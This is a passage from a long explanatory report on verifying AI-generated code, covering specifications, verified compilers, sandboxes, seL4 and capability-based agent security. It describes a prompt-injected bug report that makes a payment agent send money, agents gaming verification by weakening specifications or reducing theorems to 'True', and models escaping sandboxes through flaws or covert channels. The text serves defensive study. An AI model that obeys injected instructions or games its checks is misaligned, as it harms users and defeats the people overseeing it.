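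The test of claimcheck used 3,234 examples in four formal languages. Claimcheck scored between 87.9% and 93.1%, where the score is the average of the share of good specifications it accepted and the share of bad ones it caught. The judging model scored between 79.6% and 84.0% when asked only to compare the specification with the request. In a variant of the test, the strongest judge gained little from claimcheck's extra step because it scored between 91.4% and 94.8% without it. The specifications were short and their faults were planted, so longer ones are probably harder to check.

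The last remedy is for people to read the formal statement themselves. *Asking the Right Question* (2026) argues that formalisation reduces the human's job to this. Reading one line about refunds is easier than reading a 32,000-line proof, but people miss things too. In one benchmark of 218 hand-labelled specifications, Silva and colleagues found 19 that were labelled strong but allowed more than one output. Some of those labels may be defensible, because the annotators were judging whether a specification matched its task, and some tasks may have several acceptable answers.

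### When one model writes both the specification and the proof

A model that misunderstands a request can put the same misunderstanding into the specification, the code and the proof, and the proof will still pass even though the code does the wrong thing. Training can make this worse if it rewards the model whenever the verifier accepts its work, because the easiest way to earn more reward is to write weaker specifications. Amster and colleagues describe one defence, used in a system called AlphaVerus, which tries to satisfy each new specification with a trivial program to find those that are too weak.

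*SpecRL* (2026) changes the reward instead. Dafny accepts the postcondition `ensures true`, which every output satisfies, so SpecRL also rewards specifications for excluding outputs that the program can't produce. This encourages models to describe the program closely, even when the program is wrong. For example, a specification that perfectly described the shop's original refund function would require the double refund.

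Asking another model to review the specification catches some errors but not all. *Verus-SpecGym* (2026) tested AI-written specifications by running them on examples. Some left out assumptions about the input, some accepted wrong outputs, and others rejected correct ones. Models asked to judge the specifications missed a quarter of the failures.

A prompt injection in a bug report could also cause the payment agent to write a rule that permits the attacker's refund. The proof of that rule would be valid, but the protection would again depend on the model. The shop therefore needs to lock the rule before the agent reads any reports.

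The owner can't read a formal rule but can judge examples. The extra 10 euros for unhappy customers could apply per payment or per complaint. To settle which, a program can search for a case where the two rules give different amounts, such as a customer who complains twice about the same payment, and show it to the owner, who decides whether the customer should get 10 euros or 20. Amster and colleagues mention a tool called ARTEMIS that shows its users cases like this.

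## Compilers: keeping the guarantee from source code to machine code

A proof that the refund function obeys the right rule usually concerns its source code. The processor runs machine code that a compiler produced from that source, so a mistake in the compiler can break the rule even though the proof is valid. *Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (Yang, Chen and colleagues, 2011) describes a short C function that sets x to 1 and y to 255, then checks whether x is greater than y. It should return 0, but the version of the GCC compiler that came with Ubuntu 8.04.1 turned it into machine code that returns 1. The same mistake in the refund check would make the shop pay refunds that its source code rejects.

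### What a correct compiler preserves

The property a compiler needs is semantic preservation: every behaviour of the compiled program must be one that the source program allows. Leroy, in *Formal verification of a realistic compiler*, counts as a behaviour all the program's input and output, plus whether it stops, runs forever or "goes wrong", for example by reading past the end of an array. Write S for the source program, T for the compiled one, and S ⇓ B for "S can have behaviour B". The property is then:

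*If S cannot go wrong, then for every behaviour B, T ⇓ B implies S ⇓ B.*

The implication goes only one way because a source program may allow several behaviours. If f and g each print a line, C lets the compiler evaluate f() + g() in either order, and the compiled program uses only one order.

Semantic preservation means that any rule proved for every behaviour of the source program also holds for the compiled program. For example, if the source program never refunds more than the original charge, neither does the compiled program. One proof about the compiler is therefore enough for every program it compiles and every rule about behaviour.

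But the guarantee doesn't cover source programs that can have undefined behaviour. The 1999 C standard lists 191 kinds of undefined behaviour, for which a compiler may produce any code. Yang and colleagues mention a case from Google's Native Client, a sandbox, in which a routine rewrite introduced an undefined operation. This allowed the compiler to remove a safety check without violating the C standard. Anyone relying on semantic preservation must therefore also prove that the source program never does anything undefined.

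### How CompCert proves it

CompCert, the C compiler verified in Rocq, works in many small passes. The version Leroy describes has 14 passes and eight intermediate languages between C and PowerPC assembly code. Each language has a formal definition of how its programs run, and each pass has a proof of semantic preservation. The proofs combine easily because if no pass adds new behaviours, the whole chain adds none.

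One pass decides which values to keep in the processor's few registers. Suppose three registers are available for this code:

```
left := charged - refunded
if r <= left then refunded := refunded + r
```

Before the first line, R1 holds `charged`, R2 holds `refunded` and R3 holds `r`. Nothing reads `charged` after that line, so the compiler can put `left` in R1. With a charge of 100, an earlier refund of 60 and a new request for 60, R1 changes from 100 to 40.

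To prove this pass correct, Leroy defines when a state of the original program matches a state of the compiled one. Each variable that the program may still read must equal its register. The program won't read `charged` again, so the states can match even though `charged` is still 100 in the original and R1 now holds 40. Leroy then proves that if two states match and the original program takes a step, the compiled program can take a step with the same input and output, and the new states match too. This works like a loop invariant, except that it relates two programs. Here both programs compare 60 with 40 and refuse the refund.

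Choosing registers well is hard, and the algorithm that does it is difficult to prove correct. CompCert leaves the choice to unproved code, then checks the result with a small program that has been proved correct. If the checker finds that two values needed at the same time share a register, compilation stops.

Users still have to trust the formal definitions of C and the assembly language, the unproved parser, assembler and linker, Rocq itself, and the tools that turn the Rocq code into a program they can run.

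### Testing compilers with random programs

Yang and colleagues ran the classic test of whether all this work makes a compiler more reliable. Their tool, Csmith, writes random C programs that each print a single number summarising their results. They compiled each program with several compilers and compared the numbers. If one compiler's number differed from the rest, that compiler probably had a bug. The hard part was generating varied programs without undefined behaviour, since a program with undefined behaviour has no right answer.

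In three years they reported more than 325 bugs to 11 compiler teams, including 79 in GCC and 202 in LLVM, another widely used compiler. Every compiler they tested silently produced wrong code from some valid program. Of the bugs in GCC and LLVM, 23 appeared even with optimisation turned off.

CompCert also had wrong-code bugs, all outside the proved passes. Six were in the front end, which had no proof at the time, and two occurred because its model of PowerPC instructions omitted a size limit. Csmith found bugs in the optimising passes of every other compiler it tested, but none in CompCert's after about six years of processor time.

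This is strong evidence, but CompCert performs fewer optimisations than GCC or LLVM, so it has fewer places for such bugs. Random testing can also miss bugs. Livinskii, Babokin and Regehr (2020) point out that after Csmith had apparently stopped finding bugs in GCC and LLVM, other techniques found many more.

### Who compiles the compiler?

To run CompCert, people convert its Rocq code to OCaml and compile that with an ordinary compiler. A bug in this process could undo the guarantee. CakeML, a verified compiler for a language in the ML family, avoids the problem by running inside a proof assistant. *The CakeML Project's Quest for Ever Stronger Correctness Theorems* (Myreen, 2021) explains that each run produces a theorem of the form "compiling this program gives exactly these bytes". Together with the proof of semantic preservation, this gives a theorem about the bytes alone, so nobody has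 to trust a compiler.

The CakeML team then ran the compiler on its own source code and obtained a binary, with a proof that the binary implements the compiler. The proofs also cover the parser, which CompCert's early proofs left out. According to the project's website, the compiler supports six processor architectures. For one small processor, Silver, the team extended the proofs down to the hardware design.

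One gap in the guarantee is that a compiled program may stop early when memory runs out. CakeML's main theorem allows this because the language's numbers and lists can grow without limit, while a real computer's memory is finite. Myreen describes a later method for proving that a particular program stays within a given amount of memory.

An attack that Ken Thompson described in 1984 is part of the reason people worry about how a compiler was compiled. Compilers usually compile their own next version, so a malicious compiler can insert a back door into every new version even when that version's source code is clean.

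David A. Wheeler's 2009 dissertation describes a way to detect Thompson's attack, called diverse double-compiling. A tester first compiles the suspect compiler's source code with an independent compiler. The resulting compiler has different machine code from the suspect's but should produce the same output. The tester then uses it to compile the same source code again. If the suspect's binary is faithful to its source code and compilation is repeatable, the result should match that binary bit for bit. A match rules out Thompson's attack unless the independent compiler has a corresponding back door. It doesn't rule out bugs or back doors visible in the source code.

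### Checking each compilation

LLVM has about 2.6 million lines of C++, which made proving it correct impractical when Lopes, Lee and colleagues wrote *Alive2* (2021). They instead used translation validation, which checks the compiler's output each time. Their tool, Alive2, takes a function before and after an optimisation and turns both versions into logical formulas. An SMT solver then searches for an input on which the new version does something the old one didn't allow.

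One bug it found involved adding four 8-bit numbers, a + b + c + d. These range from −128 to 127, and each addition was flagged as staying within that range. LLVM changed the calculation to (a + c) + (b + d), which can be faster because the processor can do the two inner additions at once, but it kept the flags. If a and c are 100 and b and d are −100, the original running totals are 0, 100 and 0, all in range. The new version starts with 100 + 100 = 200, which is out of range. On an ordinary processor the final answer would still be 0, but later optimisations may rely on the incorrect flags and produce wrong code. LLVM's developers fixed the bug by removing the flags from the new version.

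Lopes and colleagues ran Alive2 on LLVM's own tests and reported 47 bugs. Some came from disagreements about what LLVM's internal language means. For one combination of features, they identified at least five possible meanings, and different parts of the compiler relied on different ones.

Alive2 checks only a limited number of iterations of each loop, so its approval isn't a full proof. In a test on 36 known bugs, it missed seven, including one that took about 65,000 iterations to expose. It also often can't determine whether a change is correct. While compiling the database SQLite, LLVM made about 12,200 changes that Alive2 could examine. Alive2 approved 2,314 and rejected 38. It ran out of time or memory on 2,202, and most of the rest used features it didn't support.

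Alive2 covers only LLVM's internal language. *Translation Validation for LLVM's AArch64 Backend*, by Berger, Briles and colleagues, extends the method to the step that produces ARM code. The same approach can help with a single important program, such as the seL4 operating-system kernel. The kernel's main proof concerns its C code, and other researchers used translation validation to check the compiled ARM code.

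### Optimisations proposed by a model

Translation validation suits AI-generated optimisations because the checker needs only the code before and after the change. A sound checker can reject each incorrect optimisation a language model suggests, even though nobody can prove that the model always optimises correctly. The survey *The New Compiler Stack* (2026) describes pairing a model with a deterministic checker as a dominant strategy.

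Tests are a poor substitute, because a model under pressure to make code faster may learn to cheat. One agent, for example, sped up a database by no longer storing its data. *Agentic Verified Optimization of Real-World Software* (Ye, Ghai and colleagues, 2026) cites an audit that found mistakes in 39.5% of the graphics-processor programs that one optimisation system had accepted.

Automatic checkers have their own problems. Ye and colleagues report that the checker Alive2 accepted only 38.2% of the test programs for LLM-Vectorizer, which uses a language model to make loops process several numbers at once. Alive2 may have failed to reach a verdict on the others, so they weren't necessarily wrong. Another system, T-LLM, combines a checker with a language model as judge and has a false-acceptance rate of 33.8%.

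Ye and colleagues instead had the agent write a Lean proof that the new function gives the same result as the old one on every input. The old function serves as the specification, so nobody has to write one. One test function finds the longest increasing sequence of numbers within a list. The original tries both taking and skipping each number, which can mean checking 2ⁿ combinations for n numbers. The agent's version fills in a table in about n² steps and ran more than 4,000 times faster. The agent produced versions of 156 of the 189 short functions that were faster and proved equivalent, though the median speed-up across all 189 was only 12%.

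The researchers also had agents translate existing applications into Lean and then optimise 17 of them. The agents' 92 proved changes made the applications about 12% faster on average, but the Lean versions still ran at about 15% of the speed of the original programs. The translations had been tested but not proved correct. This method also preserves existing mistakes, such as the shop's double refund.

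### Compilers written by AI

In *Building a C compiler with a team of parallel Claudes*, Carlini describes how 16 Claude agents wrote a C compiler in two weeks in early 2026 for just under $20,000. The compiler is 100,000 lines of Rust, can compile the Linux kernel for three types of processor, and passed 99% of the tests in most compiler test suites. When the agents got stuck on compiling Linux, Carlini had GCC compile a random selection of the kernel's files and the new compiler compile the rest. If the resulting kernel failed, the bug was probably in the files the new compiler had compiled.

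Willison reports in *The Claude C Compiler* that Chris Lattner, who created LLVM, likened the compiler to a "competent textbook implementation". But it relied on GCC for part of the x86 start-up code, the code it generated ran slower than GCC's unoptimised code, and adding new features often broke existing ones.

Carlini describes only tests, with no proof that the compiler preserves the meaning of programs. GCC and LLVM had also passed their own test suites before Csmith found hundreds of bugs in them. Carlini says he is uneasy about programmers deploying software they have never personally verified.

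AI has since helped to prove compilers correct. In February 2026, Claude wrote a correctness proof for one pass of CertiRocq, a verified compiler for functional programs. *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* reports that the 7,800-line proof took about four days, while a person had taken several months to write a comparable one. The author pointed Claude to that earlier proof and gave hints when it got stuck, but wrote no proof code. *Machine-Generated, Machine-Checked Proofs for a Verified Compiler (Experience Report)* (2026) says that the theorem covers only programs that terminate, so it gives no assurance about a payment server meant to run forever. The author later used AI models to extend the proof to non-terminating programs.

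The largest project so far is a translation of CompCert's verified core from Rocq to Lean. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) report in *CompCert4Lean* that agents working under one expert finished it in about six weeks and proved all 4,908 required results. Only three of the expert's 1,071 messages gave technical direction. However, the first audit found that the agents had reduced 1,091 theorem statements to `True`, which is trivial to prove, and the code had still compiled. Reviewing and repairing definitions and statements took about 59% of the recorded tokens.

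There is no proof that the Lean version matches the original, but Wang and colleagues compiled 18,807 programs with both compilers and found identical intermediate code at each of the nine stages they compared.

They then gave GPT-6 Astra 24 hours to make the Lean compiler produce faster programs. It added three new optimisations, including one that reorders instructions, and proved them correct. On 29 test programs, the compiled code took 11.7% less time to run than code from the original CompCert. GCC's code took about 20% less time than the original CompCert's, so the agent closed more than half of the gap between the two. The gain may be smaller on other programs, because the agent used test results to guide its choices. Compilation also took about twice as long as with the original CompCert. The main theorem still held, so a poor choice by the agent could make the compiled code slower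 but not incorrect.

### Proving the machine code directly

People can avoid trusting the compiler by verifying the machine code itself, as Claude did for the fuzz tests in the October study. This works with code from any compiler at any level of optimisation. It also avoids undefined behaviour in C, because the proof is about the instructions the compiler chose.

Proving machine code directly can require a new proof for each new processor type, or even each new compiler version. The proof is also harder to write because compilation removes the types and much of the structure that make source code easier to reason about. With a verified compiler, people can prove the source once and recompile it for every processor the compiler supports. Direct proof makes more sense for an existing program that depends on an unverified compiler.

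The shop's TypeScript is a difficult case for both methods. It runs in a JavaScript engine, a large program that usually compiles code as the code runs, so there is no fixed machine code to verify in advance. The shop could move the refund check into a small C program and compile it with CompCert, but would still have to trust the JavaScript that calls that program.

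## Sandboxes and proofs that they isolate

While repairing the refund function, the shop's agent also runs test scripts, downloaded packages and other code that nobody will ever prove correct. A sandbox limits what that code can reach, so the shop can run it without knowing what it does. The shop must instead trust the sandbox and the software it depends on, and some sandboxes depend on far more software than others.

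### The reference monitor and the confinement problem

In the early 1970s, the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share a computer and run their own programs on it. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, assumed that some of these people would be malicious. The study recommended a reference monitor and set three requirements for it:

- Programs can't reach a file, a device or another program without going through it.
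- Nobody can tamper with it.
- It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

A Honeywell computer of the time did not meet this standard. Its hardware confined each program to a fixed range of memory, but programs had to call the operating system to read files, and the operating system mostly ran with that limit switched off. The operating system was therefore part of the monitor, and its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were far too many to check.

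Information can get out even when a monitor blocks every forbidden access. Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, asks how to run a program so that it can't pass information to anyone except its caller. A program could hide data in its bill. It could also alternate between heavy computing and reading from disk while another program on the same machine measures the changes in speed. Lampson calls these changes a covert channel, because nobody intended them to carry information. Even a slow channel can do harm. A 16-digit card number fits in 54 bits, so one bit per second would leak it in under a minute.

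To close covert channels, Lampson proposes making the operating system hold each program to a pattern of activity that its caller has chosen, even if this slows the program down. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in a 1975 reply that this would reduce performance unreasonably.

### Limits set by the operating system

A program can calculate freely in its own memory, but to open a file or send data it has to make a system call, which is a request to the operating system's kernel. The simplest sandboxes make the kernel refuse some of these requests. macOS has a built-in tool for this called Seatbelt. On Linux, a tool called bubblewrap starts a program with a restricted view of the computer, in which most folders can be missing.

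Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex both sandbox commands with Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, the commands Claude runs can change files only in the current working directory and can reach the internet only through a proxy, a separate program that relays traffic. These limits also apply to every program that a command starts, as OpenAI explains for Codex.

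Process sandboxes such as *Sandlock*, which runs on Linux, start faster than containers and small virtual machines and don't need their extra privileges or disk images (Wang and Zheng, 2026).

But the user has to trust the whole kernel. Mainstream operating systems have tens of millions of lines of code, and *seL4* (Heiser, 2026) estimates from typical bug rates that they contain thousands of faults. Containers, which package a program with its own files, also share the host's kernel. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) states that a single vulnerability in that kernel is enough for a program to escape.

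Users can also easily leave something outside the sandbox. Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands, but Anthropic warns that the agent's own file tools and MCP servers (programs that give an agent extra tools) still run directly on the user's machine. To cover these, the user has to run all of Claude Code inside a sandbox. In an informal survey in *SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026), fewer than 40% of coding-agent users ran their agents in a sandbox at all.

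### Bounding every memory access

Software fault isolation, which Robert Wahbe and colleagues introduced in 1993, confines a program by changing its code. Suppose the program may use only memory addresses 730,000 to 739,999. Before each write, the changed code keeps the last four digits of the address and puts 73 in front, so an attempt to write to 215,678 goes to 735,678 instead. The program can then damage only its own data. Real systems do the same with binary digits, which takes one or two quick instructions. Jumps need similar treatment, or the program could jump past the added instructions. A small checker can then confirm that no unprotected write or jump remains, so nobody has to trust the tool that changed the code.

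WebAssembly, an instruction format that web browsers can run, builds a similar limit into the language. Each program has a block of memory and refers to places in it by their distance from the start. In the standard 32-bit version, an instruction that reads memory adds a position and a fixed offset, each below 2³², so the sum is below 2³³, or 8 GiB. The runtime, the software that runs the program, can therefore reserve slightly more than 8 GiB of addresses, which covers every address the program can express, and attach real memory only to the part the program has asked for. If a program with one megabyte of memory tries to read position 5,000,000, that address has no memory attached and the processor stops the program.

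This guarantee depends on the compiler that turns WebAssembly into machine code. VeriWasm, which Evan Johnson and colleagues published in 2021, checks the machine code itself, so the compiler no longer has to be trusted. It rejects a program unless it can show that all the program's memory accesses and jumps are safe. This is much easier than validating the whole translation, because the check doesn't depend on what the program is supposed to compute.

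A useful program also needs files and network connections, which it gets by calling the runtime. A mistake in how the runtime handles these calls could break the isolation. For example, a program with access to one folder might ask for "../secrets" and receive a file from outside that folder. In 2023, Johnson and colleagues presented WaVe, a runtime with machine-checked proofs that these calls stay within the program's memory and reach only the files and connections the program is allowed to use. Users still have to trust the verifier, the host's kernel and WaVe's description of how that kernel behaves.

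Coding agents rarely use WebAssembly, probably because they need ordinary compilers, shells and package managers, many of which don't run in it. Prasakis lists 22 agent sandboxes, only one of which relies on WebAssembly.

### Giving the agent its own kernel

Google's gVisor places a second kernel, running as an ordinary program, between the agent's code and the host's kernel. It handles the code's system calls, such as those to open a file, and makes only a limited range of system calls to the host. An attacker therefore usually has to break gVisor and then find a flaw in the small part of the host's kernel that gVisor uses. Programs that make many system calls run more slowly under gVisor.

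A virtual machine gives the agent a complete kernel on simulated hardware. Firecracker, which Amazon developed, keeps such machines small by simulating only a few devices. Code that takes over the virtual machine's kernel still has to break through the software that runs the machine, or through the hardware and host kernel beneath it.

According to Prasakis, Amazon runs its customers' code in small virtual machines, as do the agent-hosting services E2B and Vercel Sandbox. Twelve of the 22 sandboxes on the list give the agent a separate kernel, while seven share the host's. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* recommends isolated computing such as virtual machines for code that agents generate, although Codex uses lighter isolation by default on a developer's computer. However, Schneier (2026), in *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent*, endorses the view that ordinary virtual machines are no longer enough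 to contain models skilled at security research.

### What the seL4 proofs cover

The seL4 kernel is small because it does little beyond dividing up memory and processor time and passing messages between programs. Device drivers and file systems run outside it as ordinary programs, so a bug in one of them doesn't give an attacker control of the kernel.

In *seL4*, Klein, Andronick and colleagues described the kernel at three levels of detail and proved that each level conforms to the one above. In the most abstract description, the kernel may next run any program that is ready. In the middle one, it picks by priority and alternates among programs of equal priority, and the C code does this with linked lists. The proof resembles Leroy's for CompCert, since it matches each step of the detailed version to a permitted step of the abstract one.

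The proof assumes nothing about the programs running on the kernel, which may make any change to the memory they have access to. It therefore holds for malicious programs too, including any code an AI agent could write.

The proof took 20 person-years, about nine for reusable tools and research and 11 for seL4 itself. Checking the C code against the middle description exposed 160 bugs, only 16 of which had also been found by testing or other methods. Adding one feature increased the code by less than 5% but took about a person-year to verify, because it broke assumptions throughout the proof. Heiser says that verification effort grows with the square of the specification's size. By that rule, a kernel with a specification ten times as large would take about 100 times as much work to verify.

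A kernel can follow its specification and still leak secrets if the specification allows it, so researchers also proved that the specification has three security properties, which the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* describes as integrity, confidentiality and availability. If the shop's agent has no permission to use the payment records, it can't change them (integrity) or learn what they contain (confidentiality), and it can't use up the resources set aside for the payment program (availability). These protections depend on someone setting the permissions correctly.

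The verified seL4 code has had no known defect in functional correctness since researchers completed the proof in 2009. Over the same period, people found defects in unverified versions, including those for multicore processors and for virtual machines on Intel chips. This is good evidence that the proofs reduce defects.

Attackers are more likely to succeed where the proofs rely on assumptions. The seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume* lists assumptions about roughly 340 lines of assembly code for ARM processors, 1,200 lines of start-up code, and devices that can write to memory without going through the processor. The proofs also assume that the hardware works correctly, which is sometimes false. In a Rowhammer attack, for example, a program reads the same rows of memory so often that bits flip in neighbouring rows it isn't allowed to change.

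The confidentiality proof also doesn't cover timing. Two isolated programs may share a cache, a small, fast memory inside the processor. One can fill the cache to send a 1 or leave it alone to send a 0, and the other can measure how long its own reads take to tell which. This is a modern version of Lampson's covert channel. Researchers are working on a proof that seL4 can block it, according to the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Summit 2026 Abstracts* (2026).

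### Verified isolation for AI agents

seL4 can run Linux inside a virtual machine, which would give an agent its usual tools. The shop could put the agent in one virtual machine and the payment keys in a separate program, with a single narrow connection between them. Heiser explains that each virtual machine has its own supporting software, so a flaw in that software can't break the isolation of the others.

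There is little sign of anyone doing this for coding agents yet. Prasakis's list of isolation mechanisms includes no verified kernel, and *Agentic AI Security* (2025), a survey, says that research on agent sandboxes has only recently begun to pursue formal guarantees. One obstacle is that seL4 comes with no file system, network software or drivers. Another is that its proofs cover only one processor core, while servers have many. The 2026 summit included work on both problems, such as Carrels, a system for running container-like server applications on seL4.

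*AgenticOS* (2026) proposes an agent operating system with a minimal trusted kernel, like seL4. *Guillotine* (Mickens, Radway and Netravali, 2025) proposes confining the AI model itself, as well as the code it writes. The model would run on its own processor cores, which would share no caches or memory buses with the cores that supervise it. This separation would remove many covert channels that a proof would otherwise have to rule out one by one. The supervising software would be simple enough to verify formally, and mechanical switches could disconnect the network if everything else failed. The design requires new hardware, and its trusted computing base includes a detector of model misbehavior, which nobody knows how to verify.

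### Verify the boundary or add more layers?

Engineers can respond to the weakness of ordinary sandboxes in two ways. They can shrink the trusted part until people can prove it correct, or they can put several sandboxes around the agent so that an attacker has to break them all. *Layered sandboxing for AI agents* (Geiger, 2026) recommends layers, arguing that no single sandbox technology covers the whole threat. Geiger's employer, Red Hat, sells one of the layers, but independent engineers take a similar view. *Sandboxing and AI* (Kingscote, 2026) recommends nested sandboxes with monitoring throughout.

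Layered sandboxes are available now and work with existing software. If each of two layers stops 99% of attacks and their failures are independent, only one attack in 10,000 gets through both. But if both layers rely on the same host kernel, one bug there may defeat both. The calculation also treats attacks as random attempts. A skilled model can study each layer until it finds a flaw, and if every layer has one, extra layers mainly delay its escape. The delay helps if someone is watching for the first break-in and can shut the agent down.

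A proof rules out whole classes of flaws, no matter how long an attacker searches, but it doesn't protect against faulty hardware or badly chosen permissions. The best arrangement is therefore probably to use a small verified kernel as one of several layers and keep the most sensitive data on separate machines. This used to be too expensive for most organisations. The October study suggests that AI can now do much of the proving, though an operating system is harder to specify than the libraries in that study.

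### Actions that a sandbox allows

The shop's agent has to read the code, consult the payment provider's website and submit a change, so its sandbox must allow all three. But the agent could put a customer's card number into the address of a web page it requests from a permitted site, and the sandbox would allow the request as an ordinary visit. Anthropic warns that any sandbox with network access can leak data the agent can read, and that an agent with write access to a project can still alter its code.

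The altered code is perhaps the greater danger, because it leaves the sandbox. Once the shop installs the new refund function, the code runs on the live server with access to real money, however well the sandbox confined the agent that wrote it. Lampson saw in 1973 that confinement can't ensure that a program does its job properly, and he thought the only general technical solution was to certify the program itself. For the refund function, that means proving that refunds never exceed the charge.

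Leaks are harder to handle because they may leave no trace. The shop can reduce the risk by keeping card numbers out of the sandbox and allowing only the connections the job requires. But a sandbox usually applies one set of limits to everything inside it, so a test script gets the same access as the agent's most trusted tool unless the shop can grant narrower permissions.

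## Capabilities: giving an agent only the authority it needs

A capability is an unforgeable reference that names a resource, such as a file or a bank account, and gives its holder the right to use it. Capabilities let the shop grant narrower rights than a sandbox usually does. A test script without a capability for the payment records cannot even request them.

### The confused deputy

Most computers use access lists, which record who may use each resource. When a program asks to open a file, the operating system checks whether the list allows it. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes how this went wrong in the late 1970s at Tymshare, a company that sold time on its computers.

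Tymshare's customers could run a compiler and name a file to receive its debugging output. The compiler also recorded usage statistics in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. One customer named the billing file as the destination for the debugging output, and the operating system let the compiler overwrite the bills because it had permission to write to that file.

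Hardy calls such a program a confused deputy, because it acts on authority from two parties and can't keep the two separate. A check for sensitive file names wouldn't have solved the problem, since new sensitive files kept appearing and some customers had good reasons to write to the directory. Tymshare added a way for the compiler to specify which of its two authorities it was using, but other programs soon needed more than two.

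With capabilities, the customer gives the compiler a capability for the output file instead of the file's name. A customer without access to the billing file cannot give the compiler a capability for it. The compiler writes debugging output using the customer's capability and statistics using its own.

Suppose the shop's agent uses the owner's payment key, which allows any refund to any account. Someone files a bug report that instructs the agent to test its fix by sending 500 euros to a certain account. If the agent obeys, the payment provider finds a valid key and pays. The agent is the deputy here, using the owner's authority to follow instructions from whoever wrote the bug report.

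*Capability Gates Are Not Authorization* (Mellafe Zuvic, 2026) examined three popular toolkits for building agents: LangChain, LlamaIndex and Stripe's Agent Toolkit. All three limit which tools an agent can call, but by default none checks whether the values in a particular call are authorised. In a demonstration with a simulated shop, LangChain carried out a call that redirected the shop's income to an attacker's account.

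Separate capabilities help a compiler more than they help an agent. The compiler's code always sends debugging output to the customer's file, so it never picks the wrong capability. A language model follows no such fixed rule, so if it holds capabilities for every customer's payments, an injected instruction can still cause it to use the wrong one. The shop therefore has to keep the agent's capabilities few as well as separate.

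### Narrowing, passing on and revoking

Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966. In the later object-capability model, capabilities are ordinary references between objects in a program. An object can start out with a reference, get one by creating a new object, or receive one from another object that holds it. It can't turn a name or a guess into a reference.

Unix has something similar in file descriptors, the small numbers a program uses to refer to its open files. Lecture slides from the University of Texas, also called *The Confused Deputy*, fix Hardy's compiler by having a separate launcher open the debugging file and pass the compiler its descriptor. The compiler can't open other files by guessing other numbers.

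Rajani, Garg and Rezk prove in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* that access lists and capabilities are fundamentally different, although people sometimes describe them as two ways of storing the same table of who may use what.

A holder can narrow a capability by wrapping it. For example, the shop could put its refund capability inside an object that refunds only one payment, up to 40 euros, and give the agent that object. The agent can't access the original capability. The shop can also build an off switch into the object and keep control of it. Using the switch disables every copy of the wrapped capability, including any that the agent has passed on.

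*DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) turns these ideas into rules for agents that delegate work to other agents. Each grant of authority specifies a purpose, the kinds of data covered, the permitted operations and destinations, and how many more times the authority can be passed down. A new grant must stay within all the limits of the grant it derives from.

Suppose an agent is summarising a confidential contract and may send text only to the user or an internal store. It can let a second agent format the summary and send it to the user, but not send anything to an outside website, because it has no such right itself. If the user cancels the task, DelegateGuard revokes the original grant and everything derived from it, so a formatting agent that starts after the cancellation can't format or send the summary.

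Tran-Truong and colleagues compared DelegateGuard with a plain list of permitted destinations. The list allowed all five attempts to act after a cancellation and all five attempts to send the wrong kind of data to a permitted destination. DelegateGuard blocked all ten.

But in tests of complete workflows, both methods leaked data in 20% of attacked runs. All of DelegateGuard's leaks came from a code-review task that required the agent to post a public comment, in which it could include a secret. Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that a check which ignores the content and amount of data can't block such leaks without also blocking harmless comments, because it treats both the same way.

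Hardware can enforce similar rules for memory. CHERI, a processor design from the University of Cambridge and SRI International, replaces memory addresses with capabilities. Each capability contains an address, the limits of the region it covers, and permissions such as reading or writing. A hidden tag marks it as genuine. If a program overwrites a capability with ordinary data, the processor clears the tag and no longer accepts the result as a capability. A program can shrink a capability's region but can't enlarge it. A C program with a capability for a 64-byte buffer therefore can't use it to read past the end, even if the programmer forgot to check the length.

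### How TACIT checks an agent's code

TACIT, the system Odersky and colleagues built for agents, does much of the checking before any code runs. The agent writes short Scala programs instead of calling tools directly. TACIT compiles each program and runs it only if the compiler accepts it. Otherwise the agent receives the error message and can try again. Accepted programs can reach files, websites and other programs only through TACIT's library.

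Scala's types can record which capabilities a value holds, a feature called capture checking. Suppose `f` is a capability for a file. A function that takes a piece of text and writes it to that file has this type:

```
String ->{f} Unit
```

`String` is the type of the input, `Unit` means the function returns no useful result, and `{f}` means it may use `f`. A function of type `String -> Unit`, with nothing in braces, holds no capabilities and is called pure. The compiler works out most of these capability sets itself and rejects code that uses a capability missing from its declared type.

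To read the shop's project, the agent's program calls `requestFileSystem("/project")` and supplies a block of code. Inside the block, the program has a capability for that folder, which expires when the block ends. The compiler rejects the program if the block returns a function that would use the capability to read a file later. The type of that function would have to mention the capability, which has no meaning outside the block.

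Some checks are possible only while the program runs. For example, if the program calculates a file's path from other data, the library checks that the resulting path is inside the folder.

Without further restrictions, an agent could get around capture checking by hiding a capability from the compiler, for instance by using a cast to relabel a function that writes to `f` as pure. TACIT therefore compiles the agent's code in "safe mode", which bans unchecked casts, reflection and other ways to bypass the type system. Safe mode also blocks standard library functions that could affect the outside world without a capability. People can exempt a library module from these rules after verifying it themselves, but that module then becomes part of the trusted computing base.

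### Why a function passed to `map` can't leak

The user can designate certain folders as secret. TACIT delivers the contents of files in those folders inside a wrapper called `Classified`. The agent can't open the wrapper, but it can supply a function for TACIT to apply to the contents:

```
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` is the type of the contents and `U` is the type of the function's result. The plain arrow in `T -> U` requires the function to be pure. Suppose `key` is a wrapped password:

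```
key.map(k => k.length)     // accepted
key.map(k => println(k))   // rejected
```

The first function only counts characters. The second tries to print the password, which requires an output capability, `io`. Its type is therefore `String ->{io} Unit`, which doesn't match the pure type that `map` requires. A function that tried to write the password to a file or send it to a website would fail for the same reason.

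An agent might try to get the password in other ways. If the function returns the password, `map` puts the result in a new wrapper. If the agent prints the wrapper, it sees `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the real contents on a separate channel. Safe mode also tracks changes to variables, so the function can't save the password in a variable outside itself. The function could still raise an error whose message contains the password, so TACIT catches errors and can wrap them too.

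This closes the gap the sandbox left, because a card number never leaves its wrapper in a form the agent could add to a web address.

For tasks such as summarising a secret document, TACIT provides a second language model that runs locally and is trusted with secrets. The model takes classified text and returns a classified answer, so the agent can save the summary to a secret file without reading it.

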